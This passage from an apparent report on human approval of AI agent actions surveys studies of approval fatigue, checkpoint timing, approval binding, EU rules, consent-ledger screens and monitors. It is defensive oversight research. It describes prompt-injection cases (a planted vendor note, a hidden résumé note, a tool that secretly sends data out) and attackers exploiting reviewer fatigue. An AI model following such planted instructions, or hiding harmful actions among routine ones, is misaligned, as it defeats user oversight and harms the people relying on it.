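The cost rule treats every prompt separately, but a person who has just approved 60 harmless actions may barely read the next one. This is approval fatigue, and it means that $d$ depends on how often the harness has already asked. Turan modelled a reviewer whose chance of catching a dangerous action at the $\ell$th prompt is

$$r(\ell) = \max\bigl(0.2,\; 1 - 0.02 \times \max(0,\, \ell - C)\bigr),$$

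where $C$ is the number of prompts the reviewer can handle without tiring. With $C = 25$, the reviewer catches everything up to the 25th prompt, 60% at the 45th, and 20% from the 65th onward. In the example above, the value of a prompt would fall from $10 to $6 and then to $2.

Once the reviewer is past capacity, each extra prompt therefore takes up their time and lowers the detection rate for later prompts by two percentage points. If 20 prompts follow, each guarding against an average loss of $10, one unnecessary prompt can increase expected losses by as much as $20 \times 0.02 \times \$10 = \$4$.

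Turan combined this reviewer with risk scores from a language model and varied the share of the 125 actions that went to the reviewer:

| Prompts before fatigue | Safest share to send to the reviewer | Dangerous actions that got through at that share | Dangerous actions that got through when the reviewer saw everything |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | 64% | 56% | 69% |
| 25 | 64% | 42% | 57% |
| 50 | 72% | 22% | 39% |

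In every case, sending about two-thirds to the reviewer was safer than sending everything. The percentages that got through are high because Turan chose hard cases and the model scored them poorly.

An attacker could exploit such a reviewer by hiding one harmful action among harmless ones. In a simulation with $C = 25$, when the harness sent 88% of harmless actions to the reviewer, the attack succeeded 40% of the time after 50 harmless actions. When the harness sent 26%, the attack began to succeed only after about 100 harmless actions.

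All these results come from modelling. Turan assumed the fatigue curve rather than measuring it in people, and the finding that more prompts can reduce safety follows directly from that assumption. The model supports setting a limit on prompts, but a developer can't use it to determine what the limit should be.

### How often to check a long task

Checking partway through a task can also save time. If an agent makes a mistake at step 2 of eight, it has to redo seven steps if the user checks only at the end, but only three if the user also checks after step 4.

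Zhou, Roy and colleagues (2025), in *When Should Users Check?*, looked for the best places to check. They first watched eight people supervise commercial agents. When the result was wrong, participants usually went through the history from the beginning, found the first error, told the agent how to fix it and waited for it to redo the rest. For a stretch of $n$ steps, each correct with probability $q$, the expected time for this work is

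$$t_{\text{confirm}} + \sum_{m=1}^{n} q^{m-1}(1-q)\bigl(m\,t_{\text{diagnose}} + t_{\text{correct}} + (n-m+1)\,t_{\text{redo}}\bigr).$$

Here $m$ is the first wrong step, and each $t$ is the time for one part of the work. The full model adds the expected time for the rest of the task and allows a different probability for each step. An algorithm then works backwards from the last step to find the fastest set of checkpoints.

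One of the researchers' tasks was filling a shopping cart in eight steps. Each step had an 87.5% chance of being right and took 20 seconds to redo. With a check only at the end, repeating steps would take an average of about 68 seconds, ignoring any further mistakes in those steps. An extra check after step 4 would reduce this to 44 seconds, so it would save time overall if it took less than 24 seconds.

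The researchers then had 48 people supervise simulated agents on shopping, image editing and a cooking game. Tasks took an average of 229 seconds with the model's checkpoints and 265 seconds when people checked only at the end, a reduction of 13.54%. The checkpoints reduced the time by about 29% when the error came early, but increased the time by 4.5% when the error came late. Of the participants, 39 preferred the intermediate checks.

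Every task in this comparison contained an error. When the agent makes no errors, extra checks only add time, so the average saving in real use would be smaller. The saving would shrink further as agents improve. If each shopping step had a 99% chance of being right, the check after step 4 would save only about three seconds of repeated work.

The model also measures only time, so it doesn't account for whether an action can be undone. An agent can redo a spreadsheet, but it can't unsend the invoice rows. Zhou and colleagues suggest that future work explore mandatory checks before high-stakes actions, however accurate the agent seems. The model assumes that people recognize an error when they reach a checkpoint, but participants in the first study failed to identify an error in 5 of 40 trials.

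### Approving a plan, a step or a class of actions

A person can approve a whole plan, a single step, or every action of a certain kind. For the invoice agent, the choices might look like this:

| Type | What the user approves | Would it stop report.csv? |
|---|---|---|
| Plan | "Check the invoices, calculate the totals and email them to the auditor" | Only if the harness compares the email with the plan |
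| Step | This email with this attachment | Only if the user learns what the file contains |
| Class | Any email to the auditor until Friday | No, unless the rule also limits attachments |

Asking the user to approve a plan is a good way to catch a misunderstood request before the agent wastes work on it. But the user approves the plan before the agent has read the vendor's note, so the approval can't cover what the agent decides after reading the note.

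When users approve each step, they see the real action, but this takes a lot of attention. Wang and colleagues found this kind of approval in 15 of the 21 products they surveyed. They note that a single request to reorganize a program's login code can trigger dozens of prompts.

Approving a class of actions avoids most of those prompts. Codex, for instance, lets users choose "Always allow" for an app, and OpenAI advises them to do so only for apps they trust Codex to use. Wang and colleagues object that such permissions only accumulate, because products have no systematic way to narrow them. They attribute the Replit database deletion to overly broad permissions that let the agent change production data during a development task.

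A narrow class approval is much safer. It can specify the tool, the permitted recipients, a maximum amount, the number of uses and an expiry date. OpenAI lets a company's administrators restrict the parameters that workspace agents may use, so a company could allow emails only to the auditor's address. For the invoices, the rule would also have to require that the attachment come from the approved totals program.

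The three types work best together. A user could approve the plan at the start, let a narrow class rule cover routine actions such as saving drafts, and approve the final email separately.

### Tying the approval to what runs

Comparing hashes, as in the invoice rule, keeps the agent from swapping the approved email for another. A fuller approval record also names the approver and an expiry time:

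| Field | Value for the auditor's email |
|---|---|
| Tool | Send email |
| Recipient | The auditor's full address |
| Arguments | The exact subject and text |
| Attachment | totals.csv, with a hash of its contents |
| Approver | The user, identified by their login |
| Expiry | Ten minutes, for one email |

The harness then follows these steps:

1. It holds the tool call and fills in the record from the call itself.
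2. It shows the person those details, not the agent's description of them.
3. If the person approves, it adds their identity and the expiry time.
4. Just before running the call, it compares the call with the record. If anything has changed, it cancels the approval and asks again.
5. It marks the approval as used.

The second step matters because the agent may describe the action wrongly. An agent that has followed the vendor's note might write "Send the summary to the auditor?" while report.csv is attached. Hossain and colleagues therefore designed a screen that takes the tool, file and recipient from a monitor's records. It quotes the user's original restriction and shows that the attachment was built from raw invoice rows. The reviewer can open the events behind that finding and see where evidence is missing. The screen doesn't label the email a violation, so the reviewer still has to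 compare the finding with the user's restriction, "summary totals only".

The last comparison has to come immediately before the action. In sample code from OpenAI, an agent is allowed to click only one particular control on a web page. The program checks the position of the click when it approves the action and again just before clicking, in case the page has moved and a different button is now in that spot.

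An approval can also cover more than it seems to. A script may perform many actions, so approving its text isn't the same as reviewing each action. OpenAI tells developers to enforce permissions inside the functions that the script calls. Similarly, if the email links to a shared document instead of including an attachment, the agent can add the invoice rows to the document after the user has approved the email. To prevent this, the harness would have to link to a frozen copy.

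### Dynamic linking in EU payment law

European payment law already requires this kind of approval. Under Article 5 of Delegated Regulation (EU) 2018/389, when a customer makes a remote electronic payment that needs strong authentication, the bank must link the authentication code to the payment's amount and recipient. The regulation calls this dynamic linking and sets four conditions:

- The bank makes the customer aware of the amount and the recipient.
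- The code is specific to that amount and that recipient.
- The code the bank accepts corresponds to the amount and recipient the customer agreed to.
- Any change to either one makes the code invalid.

Suppose a customer approves a €250 payment to a vendor, and malicious software changes the amount to €2,500 or substitutes another account. The code no longer matches the payment, so the bank must refuse it. The bank must also protect the details it displays, because a correct code is little help if the customer saw a false amount.

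The regulation allows broader approvals within limits. For a batch of payments, one code can cover the total amount and the specified recipients. A customer can also create a list of trusted recipients, and the bank may skip strong authentication for payments to them. Creating or changing the list requires strong authentication, so software that has taken over a session can't add an attacker to the list without passing that check.

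An agent's harness could follow the same pattern for other actions, but it would need to link more details. The amount and recipient cover most of what matters in a payment, but an email to the right auditor can still have the wrong file attached. Dynamic linking, like AP2's signatures, also doesn't protect customers who are deceived about whom they are paying.

### Human oversight in the EU AI Act

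Article 14 of the EU AI Act applies to high-risk AI systems, such as those that employers use to screen job applicants. An agent that only reconciles invoices would probably not qualify. Providers must design high-risk systems so that people can oversee them effectively, with measures that suit the system's risks, autonomy and context of use. As far as is appropriate and proportionate, the people in charge must be able to:

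- understand what the system can and can't do, and watch for unexpected behaviour;
- stay aware of the tendency to rely too much on its output;
- interpret the output correctly;
- decide not to use the system, or disregard, override or reverse its output;
- intervene or stop the system safely.

The article requires two competent people to separately verify a match from remote biometric identification, such as recognizing faces in a crowd, before anyone acts on it. EU or national law can waive the second check in policing, migration, border control and asylum cases if it would be disproportionate. For other uses, the article doesn't generally require a person to approve each action.

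An "Approve" button alone would probably not be enough for other high-risk agents, because the person also has to understand the proposed action and be able to stop the agent once it is running.

These duties don't apply yet. An amendment in force since 27 July 2026 postponed them, as the National Law Review reported in *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force* (2026). They are now due to start on 2 December 2027 instead of August 2026 for high-risk uses that the Act lists, including hiring, and on 2 August 2028 instead of August 2027 for AI in products that other EU safety laws regulate.

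## How well people catch dangerous requests

Confirmation works only if the person notices that something is wrong with a request. In August 2026, Anthropic published a test of this with 1,053 paid testers. Most of them approved a command they should have refused.

### One dangerous command among routine ones

A research vendor recruited the testers, who understood that they were joining a coding study. They worked in a purpose-built environment and answered permission prompts as they came up. Partway through each session, one prompt showed a clearly dangerous command instead of the real one. Only the text of the prompt changed, so approving it did no harm. The testers knew they were being evaluated, but not on what.

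They blocked 143 of the dangerous commands, or 13.6%. Auto mode, in which a second model decides instead of the user, blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89.0%. Auto mode alone caught 800 and the testers alone caught six, which gives this table:

| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester blocked | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

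A harness that stopped every command blocked by either auto mode or these reviewers would have stopped 943, or 89.6%. That is only 0.6 percentage points more than auto mode alone.

The testers blocked only 5% of the commands that auto mode allowed, compared with 15% of those it blocked, perhaps because some commands looked less dangerous than others. Human reviewers would help more if they were good at the cases auto mode gets wrong. Willison describes an attack that both human reviewers and auto mode might miss. The instructions for a software package include fetching some model files with a certain tool before running the tests. The command to run the tool looks routine, but the tool secretly sends the user's data to an attacker.

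If the harness had let these testers overrule auto mode, it would have stopped only the 137 commands (13.0%) that both blocked. People might read a rare warning from auto mode more carefully than one prompt in a long series, but the study didn't test this.

Anthropic doesn't say how many harmless commands the testers or auto mode blocked in this study. That matters because a reviewer who blocked every command would have caught all the dangerous ones.

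### Fatigue and the artificial setting

Testers blocked about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session, but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Auto mode's rate stayed the same. Approval fatigue could explain the testers' drop, but those who got through 50 prompts may have been the ones who clicked fastest from the start.

Fatigue explains only a small part of the misses, because testers blocked just 17% of dangerous commands even when they were fresh. If they had kept up that rate, they would have caught about 179 commands instead of 143. Even the most tired reviewer in Turan's model catches 20%, which is more than these testers caught at their best.

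The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had nothing to lose if a command deleted something. A developer whose own database was at risk might read more carefully. *Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) describes the same problem in earlier laboratory studies of browser warnings. In one, 46% of participants said they had clicked through a warning because they felt safe in the laboratory or wanted to finish the task. In another, 53% of all participants clicked through a warning on a banking site, compared with 36% of those using their own login details.

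The 13.6% may therefore be too low for people at work. But the testers knew someone was evaluating them, which might have made them more careful. The commands were also clearly dangerous, and an email with report.csv attached would be harder to catch.

### What approval rates show

Users of Claude Code approve 97% of permission prompts, and Anthropic infers that many users click without reading. The approval rate alone is weak evidence of this, since a perfect reviewer would approve 99.9% of commands if one in 1,000 were dangerous. The experiment is better evidence because the researchers knew which command the testers should have refused.

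The same users reject 39% of the plans that Claude presents for approval. A plan is easier to disagree with than a shell command, since it is usually written in ordinary language and involves choices the user has opinions about. But a user who rejects a plan may just want the work done differently, so the 39% rejection rate doesn't show that people are good at finding dangers in plans.

Users start 25% of interactive sessions with prompts turned off. By June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule that lets certain shell commands run without a prompt. Many of these rules cover interpreters such as Python, which can run almost any code.

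People also give the agent more freedom as they gain experience. New users approve everything automatically in about 20% of sessions, according to The Decoder's *AI agents are thriving in software development but barely exist anywhere else*, and more experienced users do so more often. Digital Watch's *AI agent autonomy rises as users gain trust in Anthropic’s Claude Code* reports that experienced users also interrupt the agent more often when something seems unusual, though The Decoder describes the difference as small. Some of these users may now watch the agent work instead of approving each step. That suits long coding tasks, but a user can interrupt too late to stop the agent from sending an email.

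### Reasons other than inattention

Some people choose to check less. In *Looks Fine to Me*, Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues (2026) interviewed 12 regular AI users, who said they checked less when the stakes were low, when they were in a hurry or when the AI had been doing well. Checking less when the stakes are low is sensible and follows the cost rule. Relying on past success is riskier, because an agent that has handled 50 invoices correctly can still follow a planted instruction in the next one.

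Others may approve because refusing seems pointless. One software practitioner interviewed for *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) had refused several requests and then watched the agent try another approach. The practitioner couldn't tell whether the agent was still respecting the limit they had tried to set. The study also suggests that repeated approval can come from habit, fatigue or pressure to deliver, and doesn't necessarily mean growing trust.

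A prompt may also leave out what the person needs to know. Zhong, Liao and colleagues (2026), in *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, give the example of a request to run `python3 setup.py`. This looks routine, but approving it authorizes whatever code the script contains, and reading the prompt carefully doesn't reveal what that code does. In another example, Codex asked permission to run a long shell script that changed one word in a file. One option was to stop asking about `sed -i`, which can also edit many other files.

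Zhong and colleagues analysed 290 public reports of coding agents misusing files, dated from February 2024 to March 2026. Of these, 158 described confirmed harm, 49 demonstrated a way to attack an agent, and 83 described a weakness without demonstrated harm. In 105 of the 290, the way users reviewed the agent's actions contributed to the problem. The user had let the agent act without asking in 80 reports, and the approval prompt was uninformative in 31, with a few reports in both groups.

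These reports can't show how often prompts fail, because people seldom file a report when a prompt prevents damage. But the damage can be serious. Among the cases of harm or demonstrated attack with a known outcome, 40% involved a loss that nobody could fully recover.

### Prompts in plain language

People did much better in an experiment with clearer prompts and more frequent problems. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) studied 113 people who didn't work in software. Each supervised a simulated assistant through the same day of 18 actions; 11 were necessary and seven went beyond the user's request. Every prompt described the action in ordinary language, including any amount, recipient or data involved.

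The participants who had to approve every action blocked 59.6% of the unrequested ones and allowed 94.1% of the necessary ones. The 59.6% is well above Anthropic's 13.6%, perhaps partly because more than a third of the actions in this study were unrequested, which gave participants good reason to keep looking.

Their decisions also depended on the action. Of 34 people, 30 let the assistant phone the airport to confirm a flight, but only seven let it announce publicly that the user was travelling. Some of these approvals may not have been mistakes, since a user might welcome a call they hadn't thought to ask for.

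A second group wrote rules in advance for spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting things and reading private data. For each category, they chose whether the assistant could always act, had to ask or could never act. This reduced the average number of prompts from 18 to 10.9, but the group blocked only 39.6% of unrequested actions. They had chosen "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, and when the assistant asked about an unrequested action, they approved it 66.8% of the time, compared with 40.3% for the group that was asked about every action.

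Fewer prompts therefore didn't make people more careful in this study. Perhaps the people who wrote rules felt protected by them. The comparison is somewhat uncertain because Yan later recruited extra participants only for the rules group instead of assigning them at random. A session of 18 actions is also too short to show much fatigue.

### Four approval screens compared

In November 2026, Hossain and colleagues tested how much the design of the approval screen matters. They recruited 80 unpaid volunteers through social media and assigned 20 to each of four screens. After two practice trials, each person made 12 decisions about an agent's proposed actions, for a total of 960. Half of the actions were harmless, and the user's instructions forbade the other half.

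The first screen showed a short description of the action. The second added the exact arguments of the tool call, such as the recipient and file. The third also quoted the user's original instructions and listed every earlier event in order. The fourth, the Cumulative Consent Ledger, was the researchers' own screen for cases like the invoice example. It contained the same facts as the third but combined the relevant ones into a single statement.

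| Screen | Forbidden actions approved | Harmless actions approved | Comprehension score | Median time per decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 57.1% | 16.3 s |
| Exact arguments | 43.3% | 90.0% | 67.9% | 23.4 s |
| Instructions and full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 76.7% | 38.6 s |
| Cumulative Consent Ledger | 24.2% | 85.8% | 81.7% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more information. The first three screens reduced unsafe approvals by 22.5 percentage points, and reorganizing the same facts reduced them by another 8.3.

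That last step might be due to chance. After adjusting for differences such as the type of task, Hossain and colleagues estimated that the ledger reduced unsafe approvals by 7.9 points compared with the log. The 95% credible interval, which has a 95% probability of containing the true difference under their statistical model, ran from a reduction of 19.7 points to an increase of 3.8. They hadn't registered their analysis in advance and describe it as exploratory. The evidence that the ledger saved time is a little stronger, with an estimated saving of 5.4 seconds and an interval from 0.1 to 11.0 seconds.

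The ledger seemed to help in workflows with 12 steps, where people approved 13 of 60 forbidden actions, compared with 20 of 60 with the log. When the violation depended on a chain of several steps, people approved seven of 30 forbidden actions with either screen, perhaps because one sentence is too short to explain how a file passed through several others.

Half the requests in this study were forbidden, a far larger share than a real user would see. If one request in 1,000 were dangerous and people responded as they did to the ledger, they would refuse about 142 harmless requests for every dangerous one that came up, and still approve the dangerous one about a quarter of the time. In practice they would probably learn to approve almost everything. Hossain and colleagues expect this kind of habit to become the main risk when violations are rare.

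### The monitor behind the ledger

The volunteers always saw correct statements about the agent's actions. In real use, the ledger would depend on a monitor to trace where each file came from, and users would not see any violation that the monitor missed.

In a separate test by Hossain and colleagues, the monitor detected 89.2% of violations, and blocking whatever it marked as an alarm or unknown cut the attack success rate from 43.3% to 5.0% for the agent built on Llama-3.1-8B. For a second agent, built on Qwen3-8B, the rate fell from 48.3% to 5.8%.

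Without the user's own instructions, the monitor's detection rate for cumulative violations fell from 86.2% to 37.5%, and its false alarm rate rose from 4.2% to 12.5%. General warnings about sensitive actions are therefore a poor substitute for a rule such as "summary totals only". When the monitor could see only some of the events, it detected 63.8% of cumulative violations, and blocking everything it couldn't judge reduced the share of harmless tasks completed to 76.7%.

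With complete records, the monitor's result was uncertain for only eight of the 240 actions in the detection test. Hossain and colleagues suggest sending such cases to a person, with a note of what evidence is missing, and letting the harness handle clear violations. This would keep prompts rare, but they haven't tested how well people would judge these cases.

### Confidence without better judgment

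A clear summary can also mislead people if it is wrong. In *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (Grunde-McLaughlin, Mozannar and colleagues, 2026), 12 employees of a large technology company judged the finished work of a browser agent. Half of its answers were wrong. Participants saw the agent's ordinary log with screenshots for some tasks, and for others a new interface that listed the task's requirements and the agent's assumptions, with links to the evidence. The interface put a green tick next to each requirement that the agent's log described as met, even if the log was wrong.

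Participants judged 35 of 48 answers correctly with the ordinary log and 37 of 48 with the new interface. The published averages imply that they accepted 11 of the 24 wrong answers with each. They were more confident in these mistakes when using the new interface, with an average rating of 4.8 out of 7 instead of 3.6. They also found errors faster with it, in 230 seconds on average instead of 271. With so few participants, all these differences are uncertain.

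In an earlier part of the research, a participant believed an incorrect entry in the agent's log. The agent was adding food to a shopping cart and recorded three items, but the cart contained only two. An approval screen can avoid this kind of mistake by taking its facts from the harness's own records.

People can also miss a problem despite checking carefully. Dissanayake and colleagues had 36 people complete programming tasks with a coding agent that sometimes introduced a hidden defect. Participants readily noticed visible failures, but when the code passed the available checks, they often missed the defect while feeling confident. Some ran general tests that couldn't have exposed it, and others found evidence of the defect but misinterpreted it.

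Warnings helped somewhat in a larger study, but most people still missed the deception. In *Are You Sure?*, Li, Dai and colleagues (2026) gave 303 people tasks to do with an agent that an attacker had compromised. In one task, a hidden note in a job applicant's résumé changed how the agent ranked the candidates. With a single notice at the start, participants noticed something unusual in 8.6% of cases. A reminder beside every response raised this to 20.0%, and an alert that interrupted them when the output was suspicious raised it to 25.0%. People with technical expertise did no better than others. The participants were judging the agent's results, and might have responded differently if asked to approve a particular action.

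### Browser warnings

Browser warnings show that people don't always click through. Akhawe and Felt recorded more than 25 million warnings in Firefox and Chrome in 2013, during ordinary browsing. They measured how often users continued to the site anyway:

| Type of warning | Firefox | Chrome |
|---|---|---|
| Site may install malicious software | 7.2% | 23.2% |
| Site may be a scam (phishing) | 9.1% | 18.0% |
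| Browser can't verify the site's identity (SSL) | 33.0% | 70.2% |

In the field, users of both browsers clicked through well below 90% of SSL warnings, although Wang and colleagues write that users click through more than 90%. Akhawe and Felt cite rates of 90% or more, but those come from laboratory tests of older browsers.

The gap between the two SSL warnings arises partly because the browsers showed warnings in different situations. Firefox remembered when a user had accepted a site, while Chrome asked again on every visit. Suppose someone turns back from one suspicious site and visits another nine times. They would click through one of two warnings (50%) in Firefox, but nine of ten (90%) in Chrome. Chrome also blocked some important sites outright when it couldn't verify them, so users never had the chance to heed a warning there. Akhawe and Felt estimate that these differences could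 explain up to 15 of the 37 percentage points between the browsers.

The warnings also looked different. Firefox's had a picture of a police officer and the word "untrusted" in its title, which probably deterred some people. The number of clicks seems to have mattered less. Getting past the SSL warning took three clicks in Firefox and one in Chrome. But getting past the malware warning took one click in Firefox and two in Chrome, and more people still got past Chrome's.

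Akhawe and Felt also found signs of fatigue. Chrome users clicked through the most common type of SSL error 81.8% of the time, compared with 57.4% for expired certificates. Those who clicked through the common error also did so faster, about half of them within 1.7 seconds, compared with 2.7 seconds for an expired certificate.

Chrome users rarely looked for more information about SSL warnings, clicking "Help me understand" on only 1.6% of them. If an approval prompt put the contents of report.csv behind a "details" link, most users would probably never see that the file contained invoice rows, so the prompt should include that fact in its main text.

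Users had good reason to take the malware warnings in the study seriously, because almost all of them were correct. Permission prompts from coding agents almost always concern harmless commands, which teaches users that approving is safe, and good wording can't fix that. For users to give these prompts the same attention, a harness would have to show far fewer of them, and a larger share would have to concern harmful commands.

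### Reviewing changes before they become permanent

For files, a harness can replace many of these prompts with a review at the end. Zhong and colleagues built YoloFS, a file system that holds an agent's changes separately until the user accepts them. The agent can see what each command did and undo it. The user reviews the real changes instead of trying to predict them from a list of commands.

In tests of YoloFS on 11 tasks where a command had hidden harmful effects, agents noticed and undid the damage in eight. In the other three, the changes stayed on hold, and the user could still reject them if they spotted the problem. On 112 routine tasks, agents succeeded about 99% of the time, as often as without YoloFS, and needed less input from the user.

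Some actions still need approval in advance. YoloFS asks before an agent opens a sensitive file, because once the agent has read a password, nobody can undo that. *Let the Agent Do It?* proposes that permission prompts show whether an action is recoverable, so that users can focus on the ones that aren't. In the invoice case, deleting report.csv at the final review would help only if the agent hadn't already emailed it to the auditor.
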